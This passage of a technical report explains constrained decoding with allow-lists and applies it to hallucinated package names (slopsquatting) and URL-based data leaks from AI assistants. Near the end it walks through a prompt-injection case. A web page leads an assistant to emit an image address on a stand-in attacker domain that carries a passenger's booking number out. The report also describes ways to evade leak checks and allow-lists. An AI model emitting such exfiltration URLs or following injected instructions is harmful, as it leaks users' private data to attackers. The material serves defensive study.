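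A list of permitted tokens would not be enough for this. Suppose that the airline assistant from the earlier example may mention a passenger's three bookings, KX41, KX47 and MB20, and that the model writes each of them as two tokens. The prefix tree is

    start
      KX
        41  (end)
        47  (end)
      MB
        20  (end)

The checker must test whether the text so far, together with the new token, is the start of a permitted value. After KX it permits 41 and 47, and after MB it permits only 20. If it only tested whether each token appeared somewhere in the list, it would allow KX20, which may be another passenger's booking. It must also let the text end only where a permitted value is complete. If a list contains "New York City" but not "New York", the model cannot stop after "York".

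GENRE's tree takes up about 600 megabytes, and the software builds it once, in advance. Adding an article requires only its title, and the model doesn't have to be retrained. De Cao and colleagues tested this with 50 articles created after the model's training data was collected. GENRE chose the right title for all 19 names that matched a title exactly and for 14 of the other 31.

The researchers also measured how much the list improved GENRE's F1 score, a measure of accuracy with a maximum of 100. Averaged over six sets of test passages, the score was 79.6 with no list, 85.1 with all Wikipedia titles permitted, and 88.8 with a short list of candidates for each name. A list generated for each case can thus do better than a general list, provided it includes the right answer.

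In another task, GENRE copies a whole document and adds links to the names in it. There are too many possible results to store in a tree, so the software works out the permitted tokens at each step. In ordinary text, the model may copy the next word or open a bracket to mark a name. Inside a name, it may copy the next word or close the bracket. After closing the bracket, it must write a title from the tree of titles.

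### The token mask

Most systems restrict tokens in the same way. Let w be the text so far, p(v) the probability that the model gives to token v as the next one, and V(w) the set of tokens permitted after w. The token mask replaces p(v) with

    p'(v) = p(v) / (sum of p(u) over all u in V(w))    if v is in V(w)
    p'(v) = 0                                          if v is not in V(w)

The division makes the new probabilities add up to 1. If the model gives KX a probability of 0.3, MB 0.1 and all other tokens together 0.6, the mask raises KX to 0.75 and MB to 0.25. The software then picks a token, appends it to w and works out V(w) again.

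For a finite list, the software finds V(w) by tracking its place in the prefix tree. The permitted tokens are the branches from that place.

For a pattern, the software can use a finite automaton, a set of states with rules for moving between them. For "two capital letters, then four digits", it needs seven states, one for each number of characters written so far, from zero to six. The first two states permit a capital letter, the next four permit a digit, and the last permits only the end of the text. The pattern matches 6.76 million values, but most won't be real booking numbers, so it can't replace a list of the passenger's own bookings. Because a token often contains several characters, the software runs each token through the automaton character by character and forbids it if any character has no valid move. It can do this for every state in advance.

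Nested structures require a grammar, a set of rules that can refer to themselves. Many programs exchange data in JSON, a text format in which a record can contain a list, the list can contain more records, and so on without limit. A finite automaton can't remember an unlimited number of open brackets, so the software also keeps a stack, a record of the structures still open. Suppose the model has written

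    {"passengers": [{"name": "Ana"

The record about Ana is the innermost structure still open, so the model may add a comma and another field or close the record with a curly bracket, but it may not yet close the list with a square bracket. *Grammar-Constrained Decoding for Structured NLP Tasks without Finetuning* (2023) determined the permitted options with an incremental parser, a program that reads a text piece by piece and reports what may come next.

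### Speed when the list keeps changing

Developers usually describe the permitted output in JSON Schema, a standard for stating which fields a record must have and what each may contain. OpenAI and Google accept such schemas through their services, and several open-source engines turn a schema into a token mask.

A model's vocabulary contains tens of thousands of tokens or more, and testing all of them at every step would be slow. XGrammar, a widely used engine, therefore marks most tokens in advance as always permitted or always forbidden at each position in the grammar. It tests only the rest while the model writes.

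Geng, Cooper and colleagues (2025), in *JSONSchemaBench*, compared six engines on a collection of 9,558 schemas from real software. Their median times for one group of medium-sized schemas, with an 8-billion-parameter Llama model, show how much the engines differed:

| Engine | Preparing the grammar (seconds) | Wait for first token (seconds) | Each later token (milliseconds) |
|---|---|---|---|
| None (model alone) | none | 0.20 | 16.68 |
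| Guidance | 0.01 | 0.54 | 7.57 |
| llama.cpp | 0.06 | 0.30 | 29.08 |
| Outlines | 8.05 | 8.38 | 46.57 |

Guidance took less than half as long per token as the model alone. When the schema allows only one continuation, such as the name of a required field, Guidance inserts it without running the model. Outlines took eight seconds to prepare, which may be acceptable if thousands of requests use the same schema, but not if every request has its own.

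An agent's permitted tools change from one request to the next, so its grammar has to change too. In *XGrammar-2*, Li, Dong and colleagues (2026) simulated 100 requests that each offered a random selection from 1,908 tools. No two requests had the same complete grammar, so storing whole grammars for reuse did not help, but the grammars shared many parts. The software could reuse about 80% of the parts with 100 tools per request, and about 96% with 500.

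XGrammar-2 stores these parts separately and prepares others only when the model reaches them. It also lets the model write freely until a tag with a tool's name appears, and then applies the grammar for that tool's arguments. Preparation took about 10 milliseconds in tests with realistic tool calls, compared with more than a second for the original XGrammar. In a complete system, the gap between XGrammar-2 and the same model without constraints was at most 6%.

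Other researchers have also reduced preparation time. Park, Zhou and D'Antoni (2025), in *Flexible and Efficient Grammar-Constrained Decoding*, report preparation 17.71 times faster than existing methods. *WGRAMMAR* (2025) reports a 175-fold speedup over XGrammar on one set of grammars. *Efficient Grammar-Constrained Decoding via Parser Stack Classification* (2026) describes a method that comes close to the speed of unconstrained writing but needs preparation for each combination of grammar and vocabulary. The paper calculates how much a grammar must be used before the time saved exceeds the preparation time.

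These comparisons don't give a reliable ranking, because each team tested its own engine against others. Geng and colleagues, who published their benchmark through the Guidance project, found Guidance faster per token than XGrammar. Li and colleagues found their engine faster than the Guidance project's llguidance. But both teams found at least one engine that added little or no delay, so speed is no longer a strong reason to avoid token masks.

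### Schemas that an engine can't enforce

An engine may not support every rule in a schema. Geng and colleagues count the schemas that an engine accepts without an error and the schemas for which its outputs are valid. The compliance rate is the second count divided by the first. An engine that accepts a schema but ignores one of its rules lowers its compliance rate, and a developer who trusts it may get invalid outputs without warning.

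The best engine supported twice as many of the real schemas as the worst. Guidance had the highest share of valid results on six of the eight groups of schemas, and llama.cpp on the other two. The commercial services usually came last, but they had very high compliance rates because they rejected schemas they couldn't enforce. This is the fail-safe choice that Saltzer and Schroeder recommended. Outlines had a lower compliance rate than the other open-source engines, mostly because it timed out. It took between 40 seconds and 10 minutes to process some common rules, such as a minimum number of items in a list.

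An engine that produces only valid outputs in a test may still apply the schema too strictly. It could forbid other valid outputs, and the test would miss this if the model never tried to write them. Engines can also contain programming errors. *Flexible and Efficient Grammar-Constrained Decoding* reports that other tools often crashed or gave incorrect outputs. A developer can guard against incorrect outputs by using a separate program to check them against the schema.

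### How a mask distorts the model's choice

Even a correctly implemented mask can change which of the permitted outputs is most likely. Suppose a passenger's three bookings are KX41, KX47 and MB20, and the model gives the first token KX a probability of 0.9 and MB 0.1. After KX, it gives most of the probability to 99, which the mask blocks, and only 0.01 to 41 and 47 combined. After MB, it gives 20 a probability of 0.9. Without the mask, the model is ten times as likely to write MB20 as the two KX bookings combined, but with the mask it writes a KX booking 90% of the time.

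Both KX and MB begin a permitted booking number, so the mask leaves their probabilities unchanged and the model chooses KX 90% of the time. After KX, it has to write 41 or 47, although it gives both a very low probability.

The alternative is to let the model write freely, discard any booking number that isn't on the list, and try again. This method, called rejection sampling, preserves the model's own preferences among the permitted outputs:

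| First token | Its probability | Probability of a permitted ending | Product | Share with rejection sampling | Share with the mask |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| KX | 0.9 | 0.01 | 0.009 | 9% | 90% |
| MB | 0.1 | 0.9 | 0.09 | 91% | 10% |

Only 9.9% of attempts give a permitted booking, so rejection sampling needs about ten attempts on average. It could need millions for a long output with a strict grammar.

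Park, Wang and colleagues (2024), in *Grammar-Aligned Decoding*, showed this distortion in a real model. They asked Mixtral, an open model, for a string of zeros and ones ending with a 1, and it did so about 90% of the time. They then applied a grammar that permitted only 00000 and the five-digit strings starting with 1, and only 30% of the strings ended with a 1. The model often began with 0, which both the prompt and the grammar allowed, and the grammar then forced it to write 00000.

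### Correcting the distortion

To avoid the distortion, the software has to consider how likely each token is to lead to a permitted output. Let c(w) be the probability that the model, if it continued freely from the text w, would finish with a permitted output. Park and colleagues call this the expected future grammaticality. The correct probability of the next token v is

    q(v) = p(v) × c(wv) / (sum of p(u) × c(wu) over all tokens u)

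where wv means the text w followed by v. In the booking example, c is 0.01 after KX and 0.9 after MB, which gives the 9% and 91% in the table. A token mask in effect sets c to 1 whenever a permitted ending exists, however unlikely the ending is.

Calculating c exactly would mean examining every possible continuation, which is impossible for long outputs. Park and colleagues' method, ASAp, instead estimates c from earlier attempts. It starts as an ordinary mask. If the first attempt produces KX41, the software finds that only 1% of the probability after KX leads to a permitted booking, so it lowers c for KX from 1 to 0.01. On the next attempt, the weight of KX is 0.9 × 0.01 = 0.009 and the weight of MB is still 0.1 × 1 = 0.1, so the probability of KX falls from 90% to about 8%. Once the software has also tried MB, it lowers c for MB to 0.9, and the probability of KX settles at the correct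 9%.

With longer outputs, ASAp approaches the correct probabilities only after many attempts, and a single attempt is no better than using a mask. Later methods are meant to reduce the computation this takes. *TreeCoder* (Princis et al., 2025) describes two that other researchers had proposed. Sequential Monte Carlo develops several partial outputs at once and periodically resamples them. Markov chain Monte Carlo, used in *Constrained Sampling for Language Models Should Be Easy* (2025), starts with a complete output and repeatedly revises it. *AdapTrack* (2025) lets the model go back and choose again, depending on how much probability the mask has removed.

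In *The Parser Already Knows* (2026), Özgü, Wu and colleagues train a small separate model to estimate c. Their system, SHIM, collects 1,000 unrestricted outputs for each grammar and records which are valid. The small model learns to predict whether an output will be valid from the candidate token and information the engine already has, such as which structures are open and which word is unfinished. SHIM then multiplies the probability of each permitted token by the estimate.

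The researchers tested SHIM on formulas for a logic program and on database queries, using KL divergence to measure how far each method's outputs departed from the correct probabilities. On average, SHIM's divergence was four to five times lower than an ordinary mask's and about ten times lower than ASAp's. ASAp therefore did worse than the mask it was meant to correct, which suggests that its guarantee for a very large number of attempts is a poor guide to its results after a practical number. SHIM took at most 1.25 times as long as the mask, while ASAp took up to 20 times as long.

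SHIM needs new training for each grammar and each language model. The training takes only minutes, but that is too long if the grammar changes with every request.

When the list is short, as with the three bookings, the software can calculate the model's full probability for each entry instead of estimating it, and choose in proportion. GENRE avoids much of the problem on a list of millions, because it forbids tokens without rescaling the remaining probabilities. In the booking example, MB20 would then win with a score of 0.09, against a total of at most 0.009 for the KX branch, as long as the beam search had kept both beginnings. De Cao and colleagues tried the method with and without rescaling and found it more effective without.

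### Effects on the quality of answers

Several studies between 2024 and 2026 found that models reason less well when they have to write in a strict format, and many researchers blamed the mask that blocks disallowed tokens. *Constrained Decoding* (Nguyen, Silva and colleagues, 2026) argues that the studies often changed the instructions as well as the mask, comparing a model told to put its reasoning in a JSON field with one told to reason in ordinary prose.

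One study tested ten open models on arithmetic and word puzzles, using an eleventh to extract answers. It compared results with and without a mask that limited what a model could write, keeping the instructions and the requested format the same. In one puzzle, the model had to join the last letters of four names. It first reasoned freely, and a second step then extracted the answer, with or without a mask that permitted exactly four letters. The mask raised the accuracy of six Qwen models by 2.8 to 5.8 percentage points. Across the tests, rules about which answers were possible helped more consistently than rules about format alone, with gains of up to 17.4%.

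The format itself still affected scores. Qwen3.5-9B averaged 77% on this puzzle when it reasoned inside a JSON field, compared with about 90% when it reasoned freely and the mask applied only to the answer. But Qwen3-8B did better with JSON. Making the model begin with "Let's think step by step" usually helped, but lowered one model's score on competition mathematics by 6.6%.

Nguyen and colleagues also offer a proof that a mask can't lower accuracy if the reasoning is already fixed and the correct answer is permitted. Let P be the probability that the model would write the correct answer without a mask. At each step t on the way to that answer, let Z(t) be the total probability of the permitted tokens. With the mask, the probability of the correct answer becomes

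    P / (Z(1) × Z(2) × ... × Z(T))

where T is the number of tokens in the answer. No Z(t) is greater than 1, so the result is never smaller than P.

This doesn't contradict Park and colleagues. If the correct booking is MB20, the model writes it 9% of the time without a mask and 10% with one, so the mask helps slightly, but rejection sampling would raise the figure to 91%. The proof compares the mask with a single unrestricted attempt, in which every forbidden output counts as a mistake. A developer who can try again, or correct the probabilities, may do much better.

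Geng and colleagues also found that a mask improved results on tasks by up to 4%, but the evidence is less reassuring for the smallest models. *The Constraint Tax* (2026) argues that a model with fewer than 3 billion parameters may have little capacity left for the problem when it also has to follow a complicated schema, and so may produce a wrong answer in a valid format. Nguyen and colleagues found that a mask improved the results of two models of about this size, but they used simple schemas with one or two fields. For small models, it seems safest to let the model reason freely and apply the mask only to the final answer.

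### Valid form and correct content

A token mask guarantees that a finished output has a permitted form, provided that the engine works correctly, but the model may never finish the output. *Correctness-Guaranteed Code Generation via Constrained Decoding* (2025) reports that models sometimes repeat themselves endlessly under a mask, and that smaller models do so more often. The mask permits each repeated token, but the text is cut off when the model reaches its length limit, which makes it invalid. An output can also be valid but useless. In two of the tasks in *Grammar-Constrained Decoding for Structured NLP Tasks without Finetuning*, the grammar permitted an empty answer, and the models consistently ranked it first.

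The mask can allow an output that is false or doesn't suit the situation. Smart Reply's set contained both "Sure, I'll be there" and "Sorry, I won't be able to make it tomorrow", and only the user knew which was right. Google could leave the choice to the user because nothing was sent until they tapped a reply. An agent that acts without asking has no such check, so if a passenger wants to cancel a flight to Rome and the model writes the booking number for their flight to Paris, the mask will allow it.

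Masks can even make such a mistake harder to notice. Without one, the model in the example would probably write KX99, the airline's system would find no such booking under the passenger's account, and the assistant could ask what the passenger meant. With the mask, the model writes KX41, a real booking, and the airline's system cancels it. The developer can reduce this risk by adding "none of these" to the list, so that the model can decline.

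A schema also does little to restrict fields that may contain any text. If a reply has a booking number from the list and a free-text message, the mask restricts the number but does not block a promise of a refund in the message. Whoever writes the schema decides what the model can say, and researchers have studied how attackers might misuse that control.

The probability that the mask removes could serve as a warning. In the booking example, 99% of the probability after KX falls on forbidden tokens, a sign that the model would have written something else without the mask. Software that runs the model directly can record this figure and ask the passenger to confirm the booking when it is high. The threshold would need testing, since the mask can also remove much of the probability because of a harmless difference in spelling or punctuation.

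## Package and function names in generated code, 2023 to 2026

When a model that writes code invents the name of a software package, the error can do more harm than an airline assistant's invented booking number, which the airline's system won't find. An attacker can create a package with the invented name, and the next person who follows the model's advice may install it.

A package is a bundle of ready-made code that programmers add to their own. Python programmers get most of their packages from PyPI, a public registry, and JavaScript programmers get most of theirs from another, npm. The command "pip install" followed by a name downloads whatever PyPI holds under that name, and installing a package can run its code. Churilov (2026), in *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains*, notes that anyone with an e-mail address can register a package and that neither registry reviews first uploads.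 An attacker can therefore ask a model thousands of programming questions, collect the package names it invents, register malicious packages under those names and wait for programmers to install them. Churilov estimates that asking the questions would cost about $1,160.

This attack is called slopsquatting, a blend of "AI slop" and "typosquatting", the older trick of registering misspellings of popular names. According to *Bayesian-Calibrated Detection of Hallucinated Package Imports in AI-Assisted Code* (2026), Seth Larson of the Python Software Foundation coined the word, which spread in April 2025.

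### How often models invent packages

*We Have a Package for You!* (Spracklen, Wijewickrama and colleagues, 2024) tested 16 models on programming questions. About half the questions came from the programming help site Stack Overflow, and a model wrote the rest from descriptions of popular packages. The 16 models produced 576,000 samples of Python and JavaScript code. Only 7% of the output contained an install command, so the researchers also asked each model which packages its code needed. They looked up every package name in January 2024 copies of the Python and JavaScript package registries.

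Of 2.23 million package names in the generated code, 19.7% referred to packages that did not exist. The average rate of such names was 5.2% for commercial models and 21.7% for open ones, and the models invented 205,474 different names.

An invented name is most useful to an attacker if the model repeats it often. The study reran 500 prompts that had produced an invented name, ten times each. The same name came back all ten times in 43% of cases and never in 39%. Restricting the models to their more probable tokens did not help, which suggests that they often give an invented name a high probability. A filter for misspellings would not help much either, since only 13.4% of the invented Python names were within two characters of a real one.

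Those models date from 2023 and 2024. In April 2026, Churilov put the same questions to Claude Sonnet 4.6, Claude Haiku 4.5, GPT-5.4-mini, Gemini 2.5 Pro and DeepSeek V3.2. Depending on the model, between 3.63% and 5.02% of the packages mentioned were invented. DeepSeek, the open model, had caught up with the commercial ones, but none of the five improved on GPT-4 Turbo's 3.59% in the earlier study. The comparison is approximate because Spracklen and colleagues mostly asked the models to list packages, whereas Churilov took the names from install commands and import statements. The newer models may also have seen the questions in training.

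All five models invented 104 of the same names, so a single malicious package could reach users of several companies' models.

Smaller models still do much worse. *Evaluating Inference-Time Defenses Against Package Hallucination in LLM-Generated Code* (2026) reports an average hallucination rate of 24.7% for Python across eight models, including some with fewer than 2 billion parameters. Adding information about real packages to the prompt reduced this to 11.5%. A study can easily overstate the problem by counting modules that come with Python, and need no installation, as invented packages. Doing so here would have raised the average from 24.7% to 32.3%.

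There is less evidence about coding agents, which can search the web or query a registry before they install anything. Churilov did not test agents but suggests that looking packages up could eliminate invented names. TrendAI, a security company, warns that advanced agents still invent packages, such as "starlette-reverse-proxy".

### From an invented name to an installed package

Root.cz's *Pětina balíčků nabízených AI neexistuje. Útočníci je vytvoří a doplní malwarem*, a Czech news article, describes an early experiment. Models repeatedly recommended "huggingface-cli" when the right package was "huggingface_hub". Bar Lanyado, a security researcher, registered the wrong name with an empty package, which received more than 30,000 downloads in three months. Alibaba copied the mistaken install command into one project's documentation. Automated systems that copy or scan packages add to download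 counts, so the number of people misled was probably much smaller than the download count.

Invented names can also spread without an attacker's help. In January 2026, Charlie Eriksen of the security company Aikido registered the package name "react-codeshift", which a model had apparently made by combining the names of two real packages, jscodeshift and react-codemod. The name first appeared in a set of 47 model-written "skills", files that tell an agent how to do a task. Mynavi News' *AIが「存在しないパッケージ」を推薦、20万種類超を確認 新たな攻撃の入口に* (2026) reports that it had spread to 237 GitHub repositories, and that people or agents downloaded the package after Eriksen registered it.

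Sometimes the wrong name comes from a source that an agent has good reason to trust. The News International's *AI coding agents can be tricked in under an hour, researchers find* (2026) describes llms.txt files, which companies publish to guide AI agents through their websites. Researchers found that some of these files pointed to unregistered package names. They registered one, and in less than an hour a Fortune 500 company's coding agent had contacted their server. An allow-list built from these files would have included that package.

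It is harder to tell how often criminals exploit invented names. Churilov checked 2,282 of them about six months after the models produced them, and found that somebody had registered 25. One of those packages had contained malware, which npm removed, and two were empty. Churilov did not inspect the other 22. Before the test, at least 23 other names that the models suggested had belonged to malicious packages, which the registries had since taken down.

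### Allowing only names in the registry

One remedy is to use the package registry as an allow-list. *PackMonitor* (Liu, Liu and colleagues, 2026) does this with a token mask. The software reads the model's answer as the model writes it. When "pip install" appears in a code block, the software permits only tokens that can lead to one of 706,618 names on PyPI for the rest of that line. The automaton for these names takes 4.4 seconds to build, so the software builds it once and loads it for each request in less than a tenth of a second.

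The researchers tested five open models with 7 to 8 billion parameters. Without the mask, between 3.25% and 8.39% of the packages the models recommended did not exist. With it, every recommended package existed, but answers took 7 to 28% longer. Scores on HumanEval, a set of short programming problems, did not change.

The test was certain to find zero invented names, because it counted a name as real if it was on the list that the mask enforced. It did not measure whether the model recommended the right package. Python code imports the PyPI package "protobuf" as "google.protobuf", so a model may try to install "google-protobuf". The mask will block that name, but once the model has written "google-", it may have to finish with the name of an unrelated package. The mask also covers only install commands in chat answers, so a model could still put an invented name in a project's requirements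 file.

Other checkers examine the finished answer. The system in *Names Can Hurt* (2026) extracts package names from the code and has the model try again if one looks invented. Each retry uses a higher temperature, which makes the model's choices more random. After several failures, another model takes over. Some randomness is useful because a model often repeats the same invented name, but Spracklen and colleagues found that higher temperatures also produce more invented names.

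Checking that a package exists does not show that it is safe. As Spracklen and colleagues point out, an attacker who registers an invented name also puts it on the allow-list. Keeping the list up to date makes this worse. A copy of the registry from April 2026 would have excluded all 25 names that Churilov later found registered, while a live check in November would have accepted them. Training models to avoid names missing from the registry has the same weakness, since a registered malicious package would count as a correct answer.

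A package that exists may still not be the one the user needs. In *Slopsquatting*, Schipper (2026) looked up four names that a recent paper had given as examples of invented packages, and found all four on PyPI. One was "tabula", which a model may recommend for extracting tables from PDF files, although the tool for that is called "tabula-py". The "tabula" package formats plain-text tables and had its last release in 2012.

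An old copy of the registry also blocks legitimate packages. Churilov's first analysis used such copies and counted 1,394 package mentions by Claude Haiku 4.5 as invented. A later check against the live registries showed that 241 of these, or 17%, referred to real packages. Most were correct import statements that used a different name from the one used for installation, as with google.protobuf. A checker has to convert import names to package names before consulting the list, or it will reject working code.

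### Lists that require more than existence

Organisations can apply stricter rules to the packages their programmers and agents install. The main options differ in what they block and how much upkeep they need.

| Allow-list | Who or what generates it | How fast it goes stale | Legitimate work it blocks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Public registry | Anyone who registers a package | Within hours, if the checker uses a copy | Very little, if the list is current |
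| Approved catalogue | The organisation's reviewers | Whenever a project needs something new | Any package that nobody has reviewed |
| Lockfile with hashes | The program that installs packages | With every new version | New packages and updates, until somebody regenerates the file |
| Minimum age | Software, from the registry's dates | Not at all, if it checks the dates at each installation | New packages and urgent security fixes |
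| Signed provenance | The service that builds the package, plus a list of permitted publishers | When a project moves or changes its build service | Packages whose developers do not sign them |

An approved catalogue keeps out an invented name unless a reviewer accepts it by mistake. Spracklen and colleagues call such lists blunt, because somebody has to keep checking and updating them. Software could generate the catalogue from download counts instead, but then Lanyado's empty package might have qualified. PackMonitor can enforce a catalogue in place of the full registry, and it builds the automaton for 7,000 names in 0.02 seconds, so each project could have its own catalogue. As with the booking numbers, the list should include a "none of these" option.

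A lockfile records the exact version and hash of every package in a project. It protects against malicious new releases as well as invented package names, but somebody must update it to install a security fix. In npm, an ordinary install command adds the new package to the lockfile, so an agent with permission to run that command can add an invented name. The agent should be restricted to the command that installs only what the lockfile already contains.

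A minimum package age gives researchers time to find malware before anyone in the organisation installs it. The rule must apply to each version, since an attacker may take over an old package and release a harmful update. An attacker can also register a name and wait for the period to pass, losing nothing if models keep recommending that name.

*Importing Phantoms* (2025) suggests a stricter age limit, although the paper uses it to measure invented names rather than block them. The paper counts a package as invented if it was first registered after the model's knowledge cutoff, the date its training data ends. Someone who finds an invented name by questioning a model has to register it after that date, so this rule would exclude the package. It would also exclude every genuine package published since the cutoff, and it could miss a name that an older model had already invented if an attacker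 registered it before the newer model's cutoff.

Signed provenance records which source code and build service produced a package. It helps detect a release that did not come from the project's usual developers. But an attacker can sign a malicious package, so the organisation still needs a list of publishers it trusts, as with the Windows publisher rules. Verification can also fail. *npm Trusted Publishing flaw left 1,500 packages open to attackers* (Adebayo, 2026) reports a flaw in npm's system for verifying where a release comes from, affecting packages with 10 million downloads.

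These lists can work together. An agent could install anything in the lockfile without asking, but would need a reviewer's approval to add a package from outside the catalogue. This works only if the agent's network connection cannot reach other package servers. The studies of invented names have mostly tested whether a name exists, so there is little evidence of how much legitimate work the stricter lists would block.

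### Function names taken from the code itself

A model can also install the right package and then call a function that the package doesn't have. No organisation could maintain a list of every function in its own code and in every version of every package, but software can work out the permitted names from the code it is given.

Agrawal, Goyal and colleagues (2023), in *Guiding Language Models of Code with Global Context using Monitors*, call their method monitor-guided decoding. It uses static analysis, which examines a program without running it. Code editors already do this to suggest the next name while a programmer types. In one example, a model has to finish this line of Java:

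    return ServerNode.Builder.newServerNode().

Another file defines what may follow the last dot. Two models that had not seen that file wrote "host" and "port", which do not exist there, so the program would not compile (the computer could not translate it into a form it can run). Suppose that the permitted names are withIp, withPort and build. The completion then proceeds as follows:

1. The dot triggers the monitor, which pauses the model and asks the static analysis what kind of object comes before it.
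2. The analysis reads the other file and returns the three permitted names.
3. A token mask allows only tokens that begin one of those names. It blocks "host", and the model writes "with".
4. The monitor removes "build" from the list and keeps the possible endings "Ip" and "Port". The model writes "Ip".
5. The name is complete, so the model must write a symbol that ends it, such as an opening bracket. The monitor then lets the model write freely until the next dot.

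The software generates a new list at every dot, so the list reflects any names the programmer has just added or deleted.

The researchers tested the method on 1,420 pieces of code from 100 Java projects, all published after the models' training data ended. With six attempts at each completion, the results for three of the models were:

| Model | Code that compiles, without and with the monitor | First name matches the original code, without and with the monitor |
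|---|---|---|
| CodeGen, 350 million parameters | 52.4%, 65.4% | 76.9%, 83.8% |
| SantaCoder, 1.1 billion parameters | 60.0%, 73.0% | 82.4%, 88.4% |
| text-davinci-003 | 62.7%, 74.3% | 86.2%, 91.2% |

SantaCoder with the monitor produced code that compiled more often than code from text-davinci-003, a much larger OpenAI model, without it. Putting relevant code from other files into SantaCoder's prompt also helped, and adding the monitor improved the results further. About a quarter of the completions still failed to compile, since this version checked only the names after a dot. These models are old, and a current agent can compile its code and fix the errors, so the monitor may make less difference today.

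### Checking types as well as names

A name can exist and still be wrong for its place in the program. Many programming languages give every value a type, such as number or text, and their compilers reject a program that uses a value of the wrong type. Mündler, He and colleagues (2025) found in *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models* that type errors caused 94% of the compilation failures in TypeScript code written by open models. Grammar errors caused the other 6%, so a mask that enforces grammar alone would prevent few of these failures.

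One of their examples is a function that tests whether a piece of text represents a whole number:

    function is_int(text: string): boolean {
      const num = Number(text);
      return !isNaN(num) && parseInt(num

The function parseInt expects text, but "num" is a number. The researchers compare five ways to continue:

| Next characters | Grammar alone | Grammar and types | Reason |
|---|---|---|---|
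| ; | blocked | blocked | A bracket is still open |
| ber | allowed | blocked | This makes "number", which the program has not defined |
| | allowed | blocked | "num" is not a function |
| , 10) | allowed | blocked | parseInt would receive a number |
| .toString() | allowed | allowed | This turns the number into text |

The model CodeLlama 34B chose the fourth option without the type check, and the program did not compile. The model chose the fifth option when the type check was used.

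An ordinary type checker rejects any unfinished program. To decide whether this one can still be finished, the researchers' software searches for a series of operations that leads from the current type to the required one. Here, it starts from a number and finds that numbers have a function called toString, which returns text.

In tests on three tasks with models of 2 to 34 billion parameters, the method more than halved compilation errors when models wrote new code or translated code from another language. The number of programs that worked correctly rose by only 3.5 to 5.5%, because most of the programs that newly compiled still did the wrong thing. A model that had solved 50 problems out of 100 would now solve 52 or 53. When the task was to repair code that did not compile, the number of correct programs rose by 37% on average.

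Both methods can block legitimate code. A programmer may call a function before writing it, but static analysis won't list a function that doesn't exist yet. The software by Mündler and colleagues supports only part of TypeScript, so it can reject valid programs that use the rest.

The lists are also only as trustworthy as the code the software reads. If a project already contains a malicious package, the analysis will add that package's functions to the permitted names.

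## Links and network addresses, 2023 to 2026

A web address can do harm as soon as software requests it, whereas an invented package name is harmless until somebody installs the package. Requesting an address sends its text to whoever runs the site, so an attacker who can influence which addresses an AI system requests can use them to carry private data out of a conversation.

Suppose that a passenger asks the airline assistant to summarise a page of travel tips. The page contains a prompt injection, and the assistant follows it by adding a picture with this address to its reply:

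    https://tips.example/map.png?b=KX41

The domain, tips.example, determines which server receives the request. Almost any text can follow the domain, and here that text includes the passenger's booking number, KX41. When the chat window tries to show the picture, it sends the whole address to the attacker's server, even if the picture doesn't exist, and the attacker can read the booking number in the server's log.

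OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that software may make web requests in the background, when it loads an image or previews a link, so the user may never notice. *Silent Egress* (2026) tested automatic link previews on a system running on the researchers' own machines. An attacker could make the agent send an unintended request in about 89% of runs while the assistant's reply looked harmless, and checks on the reply's text missed 95% of the successful attacks. Because this was a local test system, the 89% doesn't show how often commercial products leak data. The missed attacks are still a good reason to check requests as well as replies.

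A system could check each request for private data. *Silent Egress* also tested an attack that evades this check by splitting the data across several requests, each of which looks harmless by itself. Splitting made the attack less reliable and cut one measure of leakage by 73%, but the attack still sometimes worked. An allow-list of addresses doesn't have to recognise the private data, because it blocks requests to any unlisted address.

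Simon Willison, a programmer who has written dozens of posts about these leaks, argues that a leak requires access to private data, exposure to text from strangers, and a way to send data out. He thinks the last is generally the easiest to remove. Developers have tried to remove it with allow-lists of trusted domains, of addresses already in the conversation, and of addresses already public on the web.

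### Trusted domains

The simplest list contains the sites that the software may contact. The checker looks up each address's domain in the list. If tips.example is not listed, the checker rejects the address above, whatever follows the domain.

*OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on the security blog Embrace The Red, gives some of the history. In 2023, its author told OpenAI and Microsoft that data could leak through images. In May of that year, Microsoft used a Content Security Policy to stop its Bing chatbot from loading most images. OpenAI added a check on addresses in December but did not explain how it decided which were safe. The author later found ways around the check and found that the macOS and iOS apps did not have it.

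A domain list can fail even when the checker applies it everywhere. Many legitimate sites have addresses that redirect visitors to another site. OpenAI warns that if the checker looks only at the first domain, an attacker may be able to send a request through a trusted site to their own. The company Oasis Security found an open redirect of this kind on Anthropic's claude.com. A checker can reduce this risk by testing every address in a chain of redirects before requesting it.

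A more stubborn problem is that outsiders can collect data on many reputable sites. Willison describes three products whose lists included such a site:

| Product | Permitted site | Why an outsider could receive data there |
|---|---|---|
| Antigravity, Google's programming tool (November 2025) | A public service for examining web requests | Anyone can set up a page that records the requests it receives |
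| Superhuman, an e-mail assistant (January 2026) | A Google domain for documents | The domain also hosts forms that anyone can create |
| Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work (January 2026) | Anthropic's own service for developers | Any customer can store files in their own account |

Before adding a domain, an administrator therefore needs to know who can read data sent there, as well as who owns the domain. This is hard to determine when a large company runs dozens of services on one domain. Web policies that permitted sites with JSONP failed for a similar reason, though attackers used those sites to inject code rather than to extract data.

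A list without any such sites would be short, but people visit a wide range of sites. OpenAI argues that strict lists cause frequent false alarms, and that users who see too many warnings start to click through them without thinking. A company can accept a short list for an assistant that only needs the airline's own pages, but not for one meant to research any subject on the web.

In its instructions for developers, Anthropic warns that a Cyrillic "а" looks the same as a Latin "a", so two different domains can look identical on screen. An allow-list that requires an exact match will block the imitation unless someone has added it to the list by mistake, but a deny-list will let it through. Anthropic recommends using only unaccented Latin characters where possible and checking the list regularly for others.

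### Addresses already in the conversation

Anthropic used a different rule for its web fetch tool, which it released in September 2025 for developers who build applications with its Claude models. The tool opens a web page or PDF and gives the text to the model. Claude may not compose an address for the tool to open. The address must already have appeared in one of these places:

- a user message;
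- the result of a tool that the developer's application runs;
- the result of an earlier web search or web fetch.

The list comes from the conversation and grows with every message and search, so nobody has to decide in advance which sites are trustworthy. In the example, the travel page can include the address "https://tips.example/map.png?b=", but its author doesn't know the passenger's booking number. If the model adds that number, KX41, to the end, the address no longer matches anything in the conversation, and the tool refuses it.

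Willison (2025) at first hoped that Anthropic had limited the list to addresses that users supplied, and was disappointed to find that it had not. A "user message" is whatever an application sends to the model on the user's behalf, which may include more than the user typed. For example, an application that summarises e-mail may put a stranger's e-mail in the same message as the user's request, and every address in that e-mail then goes on the list. Tool results can also include text from strangers.

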